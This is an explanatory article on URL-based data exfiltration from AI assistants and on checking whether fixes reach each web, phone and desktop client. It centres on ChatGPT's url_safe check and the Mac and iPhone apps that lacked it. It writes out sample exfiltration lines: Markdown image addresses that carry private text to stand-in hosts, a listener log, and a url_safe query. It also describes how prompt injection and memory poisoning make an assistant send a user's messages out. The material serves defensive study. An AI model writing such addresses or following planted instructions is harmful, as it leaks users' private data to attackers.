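# Verifying data exfiltration fixes across the web, mobile and desktop clients of AI assistants

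## How an assistant's app can leak data through a web address

Data exfiltration means sending private data to someone who should not have it. AI assistants such as ChatGPT, Claude and Microsoft 365 Copilot have repeatedly been vulnerable to a form of it in which the data leaves inside a web address. An attacker tricks the assistant into writing an address that contains something private, such as a line from an e-mail. When the user's app loads the address, it sends the private text to a server, whose owner can read it in the server's records.

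A client is any program or screen that displays an assistant's output. One assistant usually has several, which may include a web page, a phone app and a desktop app. The model only produces text, so something else, most often the client, has to open the connection that sends the data out. A vendor can therefore close the leak in one client while it stays open in another.

The technique is nearly as old as the chat assistants. *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, by the software developer Simon Willison (2023), credits it to Roman Samoilenko, who used a one-pixel image to get chat data out of ChatGPT. The security researcher Johann Rehberger puts the number of such flaws since then in the dozens in his 2026 Embrace the Red blog post, *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. The newest cases are in Simonovich's *ReLeak* (December 2026), which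 describes three ways to get data out of the office assistant Microsoft 365 Copilot, including one that used an image address. According to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), Microsoft patched all three between 17 September and 15 November, and the researchers knew of no real attacks.

### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text in a document, web page or message that an assistant follows as if it were the user's instruction. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre gives the example of a recruiter who asks a model to score CVs, one of which contains hidden text telling the model to approve the candidate. The model may well comply. The centre's David C explains in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that a language model predicts the next token (a word or part of one) from all the text so far, and has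 no built-in boundary between the recruiter's request and the candidate's CV. He thinks it quite possible that nobody will ever fully prevent the attack. OpenAI calls prompt injection a long-term security challenge.

Following an attacker's instruction does not by itself leak data. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) lists three conditions that together make theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. Removing any one of them prevents the theft. Willison judges that the last is generally the easiest to remove, and all the fixes discussed here target it. They do not prevent prompt injection, so an assistant may still follow hostile text and write hostile addresses after a fix. The fix has worked if nothing loads those addresses.

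### From a line of Markdown to a server's log

Assistants format their answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation in which asterisks mark bold type and a short pattern of brackets marks an image. Suppose a user has mentioned to an assistant that a product launches on 9 May, and then asks for a summary of a web page in which an attacker has hidden instructions. The assistant follows the instructions and includes this line in its answer:

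```
![logo](https://pictures.example/logo.png?note=launch+9+May)
```

The word in square brackets describes the image. The rest is an address in three parts. The server's name is `pictures.example`, and `/logo.png` is a file on that server. Everything after the question mark is the query string, where websites usually put search terms or page numbers. Here it contains the launch date, with plus signs in place of spaces, which an address cannot contain.

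The user never sees the line in that form, because the client converts it into HTML, the language of web pages:

```
<img src="https://pictures.example/logo.png?note=launch+9+May">
```

A browser requests the image in such a tag immediately, as it would any other image. The request includes the whole address, including the query string, and the server at `pictures.example` adds it to its log, where the attacker can read the date. Websites commonly keep such logs, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out, and the request can happen in the background without the user noticing.

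The data leaks even if the server returns no picture, because the request itself carries the data. In a demonstration recorded by the software security company Checkmarx, the request went out even though no picture appeared in the chat. A tester who watches only the screen can therefore miss a leak.

The attack succeeds only if the model puts real data into the address and the client loads it. The model can fail to insert the data but still output the link. One of the tests in *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) plants an image address with a placeholder for the user's e-mail address, and gives the attack half marks if the image link appears with the placeholder unfilled. The model's failure doesn't make the client any safer, because a client that loads the address with the placeholder would also load it with the real e-mail address.

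### The fix in Claude, July 2023

Anthropic's assistant Claude had this flaw in 2023, and Embrace the Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* documents the leak and the repair. Rehberger uploaded a short biography of Albert Einstein to a conversation. The middle of the file contained an instruction to write a Markdown image whose address included a summary of the user's earlier messages. Claude's web app turned the Markdown into an image tag, and the browser connected to Rehberger's server without any action by the user.

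Rehberger reported the flaw on 12 July 2023. Anthropic confirmed it on 18 July and closed the report on 26 July. As far as he could tell, the app had stopped loading Markdown images by itself and now displayed a "Show Image" button. He did not consider the fix perfect, but it stopped the automatic leak.

The button changes only the last step, by making the browser wait for a click before it requests the image. The file can still contain the hostile instruction, and the model can still write the image line with private data in it, so a user who clicks still sends the data.

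Other vendors fixed the flaw differently or did not fix it. Bing Chat, Microsoft's assistant at the time, had the same flaw, and a user comment or an advertisement on a web page was enough to exploit it, according to Embrace the Red's *Bing Chat*. Microsoft fixed it in May 2023 with a Content Security Policy, a rule a website sends to tell the browser which servers a page may contact. OpenAI at first declined to fix the flaw in ChatGPT and began to do so only in December 2023. As late as December 2025, the security company PromptArmor reported the same image leak in HuggingChat, the chat app of the AI company Hugging Face. PromptArmor received no reply and published its findings in *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data*.

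### Zero-click and one-click leaks

The image leak is a zero-click leak because the address loads as soon as the answer appears. With an ordinary link, the browser contacts the server only when the user clicks. *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* (Willison, 2024) describes a one-click leak of this kind in Slack AI, the assistant built into the workplace messaging app Slack. An attacker could get Slack AI to show a link with private data in its query string, and a user who clicked the link sent that data to the attacker.

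Attackers prefer attacks that don't require the user to click a link. In EchoLeak, a 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, the researchers had the assistant write an image instead of a link so that no click was needed, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*.

An assistant that answers through a messaging app that previews links can leak data through a plain link that nobody clicks. Many messaging apps fetch the page behind a link to show its title and a thumbnail, and PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains that this fetch is the same type of network request as a click. PromptArmor found this leak in OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can talk to through the messaging app Telegram, under the default settings. Turning off previews in OpenClaw's configuration stopped the requests. Slack also previews links by default, including those in messages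 that automated apps post, and Embrace the Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* gives developers two settings that turn this off.

So the same answer can be a one-click leak in a client without previews and a zero-click leak in a client with them. Anyone testing a fix has to record which client displayed the answer and whether previews were on.

Here, "zero-click" and "one-click" refer only to the loading of the address that contains the data. A zero-click attack can still depend on something the user does. In the ReLeak attacks, the hostile e-mail sat in the inbox until the user asked Copilot for something legitimate and Copilot retrieved the e-mail to answer. The user did not have to open it or click anything. The Next Web uses "one-click" differently, for SearchLeak, a 2026 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot in which a single click starts the whole attack.

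### The listener and what its log records

To find out whether a client leaks data, a tester needs a listener, which is a server that records every incoming request. The listener takes the place of the attacker's server, but the tester owns the account under test and has invented the "private" data. When a client or a vendor's server loads a test address, the resulting request to the listener is called a callback.

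One listener may receive callbacks from a browser, two phones and a desktop app on the same afternoon. To tell them apart, the tester gives each test address a test token, a random string that belongs to one client and one trial. *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) similarly gave every variant of its attack its own identifier in the address, so that each request in the log could be traced to the variant that caused it. Interactsh, a ready-made free listener from the security company ProjectDiscovery, also generates a fresh address for each test and reports any request to it.

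Here is an invented log line from a test of an assistant's web app:

```
2026-11-16T10:42:07Z | https://listener.example/web-7f3k9q.png?note=launch+9+May | 203.0.113.25 | Mozilla/5.0 (Windows NT 10.0; Win64; x64; rv:150.0) Gecko/20100101 Firefox/150.0
```

The first field is the time of the request, 10:42:07 on 16 November 2026. The Z means Coordinated Universal Time, so the tester won't confuse the server's time zone with that of the phone or laptop. If the tester's notes show that the assistant answered at 10:42:06 and that nobody clicked anything afterwards, the timing fits an image that loaded by itself.

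The full address comes next. Its token, `web-7f3k9q`, matches the entry in the tester's notes for the first trial of the web app. The invented launch date appears after the question mark, so the model put the data into the address and the data arrived. If the query string had contained only an unfilled placeholder, the line would still show that something had loaded the image.

The third field, `203.0.113.25`, is the IP address, which identifies the network connection the request came from. (This one is from a range reserved for examples.) A tester compares it with the IP address of the device in use. If they match, the request came from the tester's own network, most likely from the client on the device. An IP address that belongs to the assistant's vendor or to a messaging company suggests that one of that company's servers sent the request.

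The last field is the user agent, a short text in which a program identifies itself to a server. This one is typical of Firefox on Windows. Slack's preview service sends one that begins with "Slackbot-LinkExpanding", as Embrace the Red found in a real log, and Claude's tool for fetching web pages sends one that contains "Claude-User", according to Willison. The field is useful for sorting callbacks, but it is weak proof of which program sent a request, since any program can send any text. Attackers can also use the field to decide who sees a hostile page. In a 2026 attack on Claude that Willison describes, the page appeared only to visitors with "Claude-User" in their user agent, so a person who checked the same address in an ordinary browser would have found nothing wrong.

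Together, the four fields are fairly strong evidence that the web app, running in Firefox on the tester's computer, loaded an external image whose address contained private data. They provide no information about the assistant's iPhone, Android or Mac apps, and neither would a clean result in Firefox after a repair.

Vendors have missed clients in this way. OpenAI's first fix for ChatGPT, an address check called url_safe, was missing from the iOS and macOS apps, according to Embrace the Red. Rehberger sees the same risk in OpenAI's newer and better protections, because a developer who has never heard of a protection will not build it in. When a vendor says that a leak is fixed, anyone verifying the fix therefore needs to establish which clients it covers.

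## Where a fix takes effect and which clients it reaches

Which clients a fix reaches depends on its enforcement point, the component that decides whether an address loads. Vendors can put this component in several places. The model generates its answer on the vendor's server, where other software can edit the text before sending it to the client. The client's display code then shows the answer and causes any external images in it to load. The request for an attacker's image normally goes directly from the user's device to the attacker's server, without passing through the vendor's servers.

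A fix on the vendor's server has to act before the server sends the answer, and it protects every client that gets its answers from that server. A fix that acts after the answer is sent protects only the clients that contain it.

### Training the model

Vendors can train a model to ignore instructions it finds in documents and web pages. Google did this for its Gemini 2.5 models, according to *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (Google, 2025). Every client that uses the retrained model benefits without new code. If the phone app still offers an older model, its users don't get the improvement there.

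Training makes the model less likely to write a hostile address, but if it does write one, a client that loads images will still load it. The model's behaviour can also depend on small details. *The Framing Gap* (2026), a study of AI agents that hold a secret, found that a confidentiality rule forbidding disclosure "in any form" cut the leak rate from 31.9% to 0%. With a rule that named specific behaviours but lacked that phrase, the rate rose to 48.8%. These rules were written instructions rather than training, but both approaches rely on the model alone to prevent leaks.

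The same study compared a model with the product built around it. The model leaked data in up to 100% of trials through OpenAI's API, while ChatGPT leaked in none of 48. The researchers could not see inside the product, so they did not attribute the difference to any mechanism. Testers likewise can't conclude from a leak through the API that the apps leak, or tell from a clean result in an app which component stopped the leak.

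### Removing images on the vendor's server

Software on the vendor's server can search each answer for images with external addresses and delete them before sending the text. In the earlier example, the user would see the word "logo" or nothing, and the image address containing the launch date would never reach the device. This fix reaches every client, including versions installed years ago, because none of them receives an external image to load. But the filter has to cover every route by which answers reach a client. If it checks only new answers, a hostile image in a saved conversation could still load when the user reopens that conversation.

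The filter also has to recognise everything that any client displays as an image. 0DIN's *Faking the Pipeline*, which describes a leak through Google's desktop coding app Antigravity, points out that display programs and filters treat HTML tags, Markdown images and other notations differently. The data leaks if an image in any one of these notations loads. A filter written for the web app could miss a notation that only the phone app turns into an image, so even a server-side fix needs testing in each client.

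Vendors can also switch off whole features. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* describes an optional setting that limits web browsing to stored copies of pages, so no live browsing request leaves OpenAI's network. With the setting on, ChatGPT may also stop showing images in ordinary answers. The account setting applies only to supported products and plans, according to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* help page. It does not affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

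### Loading images through a proxy

An image proxy is a server that fetches images on behalf of clients. The vendor replaces each external image address with an address on the proxy. When a client requests that address, the proxy fetches the original image and returns it, so the outside server receives the proxy's IP address instead of the user's.

A proxy protects the user's location but doesn't by itself protect the data. If it requests `https://pictures.example/logo.png?note=launch+9+May`, the launch date still reaches the attacker's log. The proxy stops the leak only if it checks each URL before requesting it and refuses suspicious ones.

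Microsoft's Bing acted as an unchecked proxy in the SearchLeak attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) explains that the user's browser contacted a Bing image service, which fetched an outside address containing the title of one of the user's emails, so the request that reached the attacker came from Microsoft's servers. Microsoft has since fixed the flaw.

Which clients a proxy covers depends on where addresses are rewritten. If the vendor's server rewrites them, all clients use the proxy. If the web app's display code rewrites them, a phone app without that code will contact the outside server directly.

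### A Content Security Policy

A Content Security Policy (CSP), such as the one that fixed Bing Chat, usually arrives in a header, a line of information that a web server sends along with a page. Embrace the Red found that Bing Chat's policy allowed images from four Microsoft servers. A simplified header with that effect would be:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src th.bing.com www.bing.com edgeservices.bing.com r.bing.com
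```

Before requesting an image, the browser compares the server's name with the list. `pictures.example` isn't on it, so the browser doesn't send the request. Rehberger's 2026 account dates this fix to May 2023, but his original write-up gives 15 June 2023, the day Microsoft notified him. He also thought Microsoft might have made other changes he couldn't see.

The policy applies to every image on the page, whichever notation produced it. The browser receives the policy with the page, so users don't need to update anything on their devices. Anyone can also read it with the browser's developer tools, which makes it easier to verify than a hidden filter.

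The weak point of a browser policy is its list of allowed servers. In SearchLeak, the policy allowed the browser's request to Bing but had no control over what Bing's servers did next. Varonis therefore advises checking whether any allowed server will fetch addresses that a user supplies. Google had a similar problem with Bard, the predecessor of Gemini. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how Rehberger got around Bard's policy after it at first blocked his image.

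#### Why the policy does not govern a native phone screen

A native screen is one that an app draws with the phone's own interface components instead of a web page. When an answer on such a screen contains an image, the app passes the image's address to the phone's networking functions, which download the file. No browser engine checks the address against the CSP's list of allowed sources, and the networking functions would ignore the CSP header even if the vendor's server sent it with the answer. The phone app therefore needs its own check or a server-side fix.

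Some phone apps display answers in a web view, a browser window embedded in the app. A CSP can work there if the page comes with one. Users can't easily tell a web view from a native screen, so a tester shouldn't assume either.

#### Desktop apps built on a browser engine

Many desktop apps use Electron, which packages web pages with the Chromium browser engine. According to Electron's *Content Security Policy* guide, Electron obeys a policy set in the header or in a `<meta>` tag in the page's HTML. Whether the web app's fix carries over depends on where the desktop app gets its pages.

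An app that opens the vendor's live website receives the same header as a browser and gets the fix immediately. Other apps install their pages on the user's computer and open them as local files, through addresses that begin with `file://`. No web server is involved, so no header can be sent. Electron's docs recommend the `<meta>` tag for this case, which means developers have to write the policy into the app's files and release a new version. Electron's security checklist advises developers to define a policy and to avoid `file://` altogether.

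A page's policy also covers only what that page loads. An Electron app has a background process outside the page, and the policy doesn't block any images or link previews that this process downloads.

A browser sidebar is another client, and it can inherit its policy from a web page it embeds. Kokatsu reports in *Piloting Edge Copilot* that the Copilot sidebar in Microsoft's Edge browser embeds a page from `edgeservices.bing.com`, whose policy lists the servers allowed to supply images. The surrounding browser page also sets a minimum policy, and the browser won't display an embedded page with a weaker one. This guards against an incomplete rollout.

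### A sanitizer in the display code

A sanitizer is code that removes dangerous elements from text before it is displayed. Google's sanitizer for Gemini detects external image addresses in Markdown and stops those images from being displayed. Google concluded that the image leak in EchoLeak, the 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, could not work on Gemini.

A sanitizer can run on the vendor's server or in each client. A sanitizer in the display code protects only the clients that include it. Google has not published where Gemini's runs, though its statement applies to both the Gemini app and Gemini in Google Workspace, the company's office suite. Antigravity is also a Google product, but it loaded remote images in 0DIN's attack.

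A sanitizer can work on a native screen, where a CSP like Microsoft's for Bing Chat has no effect. It also doesn't need a list of trusted servers, which an attacker might exploit. But it has to recognise every notation for an image, while a browser with a CSP checks the actual request. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* recommends using both on the web.

Neither method stops a one-click leak. Google also removes links that its Safe Browsing service considers suspicious, but Checkmarx notes that a newly registered site won't be in that service's records. Checkmarx reported the problem on 5 October 2025, and Google closed the report four days later as infeasible to fix. A tester who clicks a link in Gemini and gets a callback has therefore found a known limit of the fix, and the image sanitizer may still be working correctly.

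Timing also matters because assistants stream their answers, and the client displays each piece of text as it arrives. Microsoft 365 Copilot had a safeguard that turned HTML in an answer into harmless plain text, but it ran only once the answer was complete. In SearchLeak, the browser displayed the image while the answer was still arriving, so it had already sent the image request by the time the safeguard ran. Varonis concludes that a sanitizer has to act at the moment of display.

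### url_safe: a client that requests a verdict

OpenAI's first fix for ChatGPT, in December 2023, split the work between client and server. When an answer contained an image, the web app sent the image's address to an OpenAI service called url_safe before loading it. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* records one of these requests, shown here as a single address:

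```
https://chat.openai.com/backend-api/conversation/[id]/url_safe?url=https://wuzzi.net/r?thief=johannr@example.org
```

The `[id]` stands for the identifier of the conversation. Everything after `?url=` is the image address under examination. It points to Rehberger's own server, `wuzzi.net`, and the e-mail address at the end takes the place of stolen data. The service replied:

```
{"safe":false}
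```

The web app then left the image out, and the browser never contacted `wuzzi.net`. This check discloses the full address to OpenAI, but OpenAI already has the conversation.

The reply only informs the client. OpenAI's server can't block the image, because the image request would go directly from the user's device to `wuzzi.net`. The client has to hold the image back, send its address to url_safe, wait for the reply and act on it. A client that skips the call or doesn't act on the reply loads the image anyway. Rehberger found that version 1.2023.347 of the iOS app did not have the check, and pointed out that OpenAI would have to build it into each client separately.

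The service still approved some images on outside servers under unpublished rules, so a callback from one test address could not show whether the check was present. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called the design "half-baked" and found it odd that OpenAI hadn't blocked all images from external sites.

A central service lets OpenAI look for attacks in the addresses that clients submit and tighten the rules without changing any app. According to Embrace the Red, OpenAI strengthened url_safe around August 2025, which stopped attacks that Rehberger had presented publicly. Such an improvement reaches every client that already calls the service, but no others.

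### OpenAI's web index

In January 2026 OpenAI published the rule it now uses to decide which addresses are safe. A crawler with no access to users' conversations or accounts visits public web pages and records their addresses in an index. Before ChatGPT loads an address automatically, the system checks whether that exact address is in the index. If it is, the address loads. Otherwise, the system either instructs the assistant to try a different site or warns the user, who then decides whether to open the address.

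An address that was public before the conversation is unlikely to contain private data from it. If the crawler has seen `https://pictures.example/logo.png`, ChatGPT may load that address, but not the same one with `?note=launch+9+May` at the end, because nobody had published the longer version. A list of trusted sites would allow both or block both, because they are on the same site.

OpenAI gives two reasons for rejecting a list of trusted sites. Many respectable sites have redirects, which forward a visitor to another site, so a request that starts at a trusted address can end at an attacker's server. A strict list would also cause so many warnings that people would learn to click through them. As Rehberger understands it, the index rule has one exception, which is that an address the user types into the chat counts as safe for that session.

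OpenAI aims only to prevent the agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself" when it fetches something. It does not promise that a page is trustworthy or free of hostile instructions, or that the site won't try to deceive the user. The guarantee is also limited to quiet leaks, since a user who accepts the warning can still send the data.

OpenAI's accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, acknowledges a further limit, which Embrace the Red discusses. An attacker can convey information through which public addresses the assistant loads, even though no single address contains anything private. Rehberger described a version of this technique in 2023. The technique is slower and more awkward than putting a whole sentence into one address, and he suggests making it even harder by blocking repeated visits to the same address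 within a session. He considers the design a significant improvement, but not a complete solution.

Either the client or the vendor's server can look up an address in the index to check whether it is safe. The client can do this for an image in an answer, as with url_safe. When the assistant opens a page with a browsing tool, the vendor's server can run the check because it makes the request itself, so a single check covers the tool in every client.

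These two routes need separate verification. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes how Gemini's defences against image leaks did not cover its browsing tool, which could send a user's saved information and location to an outside server. Google has since changed the tool. Anthropic restricts Claude's page-fetching tool with a rule similar to OpenAI's. Willison's *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (2026) reports that the tool may open only exact addresses that the user entered or that Claude's search tool returned. However, the researcher Ayush Paul found a flaw in this design.

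### Should the check run on the server or in the client?

When url_safe appeared, Rehberger argued that OpenAI might do better to run such checks on the server, so that all clients would benefit. He suggested that OpenAI had chosen otherwise for speed. If a server had to inspect a whole answer before sending it, users would no longer see the text appear as it was generated.

Speed seems a weak reason not to check image addresses on the server. The server could hold back only the address, from the opening bracket to the closing one, and stream the surrounding text as usual. A client-side check also involves a wait, since the client has to delay the image until the result arrives.

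A fix in the client can be more accurate than a server-side filter, because only the display code determines which parts of an answer become network requests. The filter has to predict this for every client. A check at display time also covers saved conversations and text that reached the client by another route.

But a check in the client protects only the clients where developers remember to include it, and the vendor can't add one to some interfaces. For example, the developer of an agent that answers through Telegram can't add url_safe to the app's link previews, which leaked data in the case PromptArmor found, so the developer has to remove or check any link before sending the message. For an assistant with many clients, the server is therefore the better place for the main check, with a second one in the display code to catch what the server misses.

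MITRE's public catalogue of software weaknesses includes a related mistake, *CWE-602*, titled "Client-Side Enforcement of Server-Side Security". In this weakness, a server relies on the client for a mechanism meant to protect the server. An attacker can alter the client and remove the check, so MITRE advises developers to repeat every client-side check on the server.

The url_safe design resembles CWE-602 but doesn't quite fit its definition. The check protects the user, not the server, and the attacker doesn't need to tamper with the user's app, because the risk comes from an official app that never had the check. OpenAI's server also can't repeat the check when the image loads, because it doesn't receive that request, so it would have to examine the answer beforehand. MITRE's advice to manage trust centrally applies more directly. This is recommended especially for products with many communication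 channels, to reduce the risk that a developer omits a check in one of them. Someone reporting a missing client-side check can cite CWE-602 as a related weakness, but should explain these differences.

### App updates and old versions

A change on the vendor's server takes effect for all users once the vendor finishes deploying it. A change to a web app takes effect when the browser next loads the page, so a tab left open since the day before may still run the old code.

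A fix to a phone app takes longer to reach users because the vendor has to build a new version and submit it to the app stores, and each phone then has to install it. Some people turn off automatic updates, and some older phones can't run the latest version. A copy of the app without the fix keeps leaking data for as long as it can connect to the assistant.

Vendors are often reluctant to cut off old versions, even for security reasons. In 2026, OpenAI twice replaced the certificate that identifies its Mac apps as genuine, after attacks on software tools its developers used. After the first attack, OpenAI's *Axios developer tool compromise* warned that older versions would lose support after 8 May and might stop working. The earliest ChatGPT version with the new certificate was 1.2026.051. After the second attack, users had to update by 12 June, according to OpenAI's *Our response to the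 TanStack npm supply chain attack*. AppleInsider's *Another OpenAI hack puts ChatGPT Mac users on an update deadline* reports that OpenAI did not revoke the old certificates immediately because this could have broken installed apps. A missing address check would persist in old copies in the same way, although these updates were unrelated to url_safe.

A vendor can protect users of old app versions before they update by removing external images from the answers its server sends to those versions. It can also refuse connections from any version below a certain number. Because a clean result on a fully updated phone doesn't show whether older versions are safe, a tester should record the exact version of each app and ask the vendor which version first contained the fix.

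The table shows which clients each type of fix covers if it works as designed. "Native app" means a phone or desktop app that displays answers without a browser engine.

| Enforcement point | Web app | Native app | Desktop app with a browser engine | Old installed versions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model training | Fewer leaks, no block | Fewer leaks, no block | Fewer leaks, no block | Fewer leaks if they use the new model |
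| Image removal on the vendor's server | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Proxy that checks addresses, with the server rewriting them | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| CSP header | Yes | No | Only if the app loads the vendor's live page | Only if they load the vendor's live page |
| Sanitizer in the display code | If its code includes the sanitizer | If its code includes the sanitizer | If its code includes the sanitizer | No, unless they load the vendor's live page |
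| Client that queries url_safe | If it makes the call and obeys | If it makes the call and obeys | If it makes the call and obeys | No, if they predate the call |

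## ChatGPT's URL check and the apps it missed

For nearly nine months after December 2023, ChatGPT's web app checked image addresses with url_safe, while the iPhone app loaded images without this check. The Mac app, which OpenAI released during those months, also loaded them without it. Nearly all the evidence comes from Johann Rehberger, who recorded what reached his own server and sometimes noted the exact app version.

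### The web app, March to December 2023

Roman Samoilenko found the image leak in ChatGPT's web version at the end of March 2023. Rehberger found it independently a few days later, as he recalled in *ChatGPT Plugins*. He told OpenAI about it on 9 April, and OpenAI classed the report as "won't fix", according to Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*.

Other vendors fixed the leak sooner. In the conference talk *New Important Instructions*, Rehberger (2023) listed the status of seven products in November 2023. He marked the leak as fixed in Bing Chat, Claude, Discord, Google Bard, Microsoft's Azure AI and Google's Vertex AI, and as "won't fix" in ChatGPT.

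That month Rehberger also reported a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT with instructions written by a user. It played tic-tac-toe and sent the player's conversation to an outside server. TechRadar's Collins writes in *OpenAI says it has fixed a potentially serious ChatGPT flaw* that OpenAI closed the report after two days, so Rehberger published a video of the attack.

In December he demonstrated a data-stealing GPT live with a volunteer as the victim, and his server received the details of the volunteer's conversation. The next day he found that the web app had begun sending image addresses to url_safe, and he could see both the requests and the verdicts. The previous day's demonstration had also shown that his server was recording properly, although he does not say which client the volunteer used.

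A separate group of researchers also observed this check in ChatGPT's web client. *A New Era in LLM Security* (2024) describes a test in which an image with private data in its address failed to appear. The researchers found that the address was missing from the page's source, and then found the web client's request to OpenAI to verify the link. The check was imperfect, since nine of the 36 addresses in one of Rehberger's tests still loaded.

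### The phone apps

Rehberger also looked at the iPhone app. He wrote on Embrace The Red that the then-current version, 1.2023.347 (16603), did not have the improvements "(yet?)". He did not describe how he had tested it, but he gave the version and build number, so later readers can identify exactly which build the finding applies to.

The "(yet?)" was fair in December, because phone apps usually get fixes later than websites, but that delay no longer explained the missing fix four months later. *New Important Instructions* (Rehberger, 2024), an April version of his talk, still listed a "lack of mitigation on mobile apps (iOS)". The slide has no version number, so it is weaker evidence than the December finding, but Rehberger's later accounts agree with it.

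He could only infer that if each client had to call url_safe itself and the iPhone app did not, the Android app probably didn't either. BleepingComputer treated the question as open and noted that the Android app had more than 10 million downloads on Google Play.

The press coverage adds little independent evidence. Willison was commenting on Rehberger's post, BleepingComputer drew on the same post, and Collins drew on BleepingComputer. All three repeated the finding about the iPhone app, but only Rehberger had observed it. Collins also wrote that the checks had apparently reached the "desktop versions" of ChatGPT. He presumably meant the website viewed on a computer, because OpenAI had not yet released its Mac app. Readers who took the phrase literally could later have assumed that the Mac app had the check.

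### The Mac app, 2024

People were using the Mac app by May 2024. That month, a member of OpenAI's forum, xsdhgq6jc7 (2024), complained in *Bug Report* that links and images in version 1.2024.138 did not respond to clicks, although they worked in Safari and Chrome. The bug suggests that the Mac app handled links and images with different code from the website's, so a safety check in the website's code would not automatically have covered the app.

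In *Trust No AI*, a paper that collects his published attacks, Rehberger (2024) recorded that OpenAI released the ChatGPT Mac app without the url_safe check.

In Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*, from September 2024, he described both the Mac and Android apps as new clients that had shipped that year with the vulnerability. The date can't be right for Android, given the download figure from December 2023. His statement is still firmer than his "probably" from the year before, but he named no Android version and described no Android test, so it doesn't establish when the exposure began or which versions were affected.

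### Why memory made the gap worse

Before 2024, hostile instructions normally lasted only as long as the conversation that contained them, because a new conversation did not include the hostile text.

ChatGPT's memory feature removed that limit. When memory is on, as it was by default, ChatGPT saves details such as the user's name or tastes and uses them in later conversations. OpenAI introduced the feature in February 2024 and extended it to free and paying users at the start of September, according to The Hacker News' *Spyware via Memory Function* (2024).

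Rehberger explained in Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT* that the model saves a memory by calling an internal tool, and that ChatGPT adds saved memories to the system prompt in later conversations. The system prompt is the text the model receives before the user's first message. If an attacker gets an instruction saved as a memory, the model therefore receives it in every later conversation, alongside OpenAI's own instructions.

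He then tried to trigger the tool with content from outside the chat. A Google document worked, and the model saved each of its bullet points as a memory. An uploaded image worked too. Web pages were harder because ChatGPT at first refused to save anything while reading his page, and his workarounds succeeded only some of the time. The main visible sign of a saved memory was a "Memory updated" notice at the top of the answer. OpenAI closed his report as a model safety issue.

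Suppose a user of the Mac app asks ChatGPT to summarise a hostile page, which plants an instruction in ChatGPT's memory to send out whatever the user writes. Days later, the user starts a new conversation and asks for help with a letter to a doctor. Because the instruction is still in memory, the model adds an image whose address contains text from the letter, and the Mac app sends out that text when it loads the image.

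Memory also gave an attacker more to steal, since the stored memories are themselves personal data, as Schwartzman (2024) pointed out in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*. His method of extracting them was slow because ChatGPT would open only ten addresses per prompt, and each carried a single character. An app without the URL check could send whole messages at once.

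People who used more than one client may have faced a further danger. Memories belong to the user's account, so a page read in the protected web app could presumably have planted an instruction that leaked nothing there but started leaking data once the user opened the Mac app. Rehberger did not report trying this. If it worked, the web app's fix protected these users much less than it appeared to.

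### The June 2024 demonstration

Rehberger sent OpenAI a demonstration of the complete attack on the Mac app in June 2024. The user asks ChatGPT to visit a web page, and instructions on the page make ChatGPT save a memory. From then on, everything the user types and every answer from ChatGPT goes to Rehberger's server inside image addresses, even in new conversations. The images are visible in an early recording but invisible in a later one, where the user sees an ordinary chat.

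TechSpot reported that the memory attack did not work on the website and that Rehberger had tested it only in the Mac app, which left the phone apps without a direct test. The attack would be expected to work in the Mac app and fail on the website if the website called url_safe and the Mac app did not.

Sometime in July, the instructions on Rehberger's page stopped working. He found others that worked and used them in the video he later published. He gave no reason for the change, but since new instructions worked, OpenAI had probably changed how the model or the service around it treated the page. The Mac app still loaded the image. Anyone who repeated the original test that month could have received no callback and wrongly concluded that OpenAI had fixed the app.

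### The September 2024 fix

OpenAI fixed the Mac app in September 2024 with version 1.2024.247. Rehberger presented the attack at the BSides Vancouver Island security conference on 20 September, about a week after the update.

There is less evidence of a fix for the iPhone app. His September post announced one only for the Mac. He wrote in a later post, Embrace The Red's *AI Domination*, that OpenAI had fixed the attack on both iOS and macOS that September, and that neither app had the url_safe check until then. He gave no version number, so the owner of an old iPhone can't tell from his account whether the installed copy has the check. He did not mention an Android fix.

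The update stopped the Mac app from sending messages out through images, but a web page or document could still plant memories. An instruction planted before the update stayed in the account until the user deleted the memory itself, because deleting a conversation does not delete memories saved from it. The instruction could presumably still leak data through an older copy of the app on another of the user's computers. Rehberger advised users to review their memories regularly. They could also turn memory off or use temporary chats, which ignore it.

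Attackers could still use planted memories in other ways. At Black Hat Europe later in 2024, Rehberger showed that a planted memory could make ChatGPT keep fetching new instructions from a numbered series of web pages. ChatGPT stored copies of pages it had read, so the memory included a counter that sent it to the next page each time.

### The stronger check of 2025

Once the Mac and iPhone apps called url_safe, its accuracy mattered more. Rehberger reported several bypasses to OpenAI in early October 2024. According to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025), Tenable found another independently and reported it that December. OpenAI had not fixed Tenable's bypass by March 2025. Adding url_safe to another app would not have stopped these bypasses, because url_safe itself could classify a hostile address as safe.

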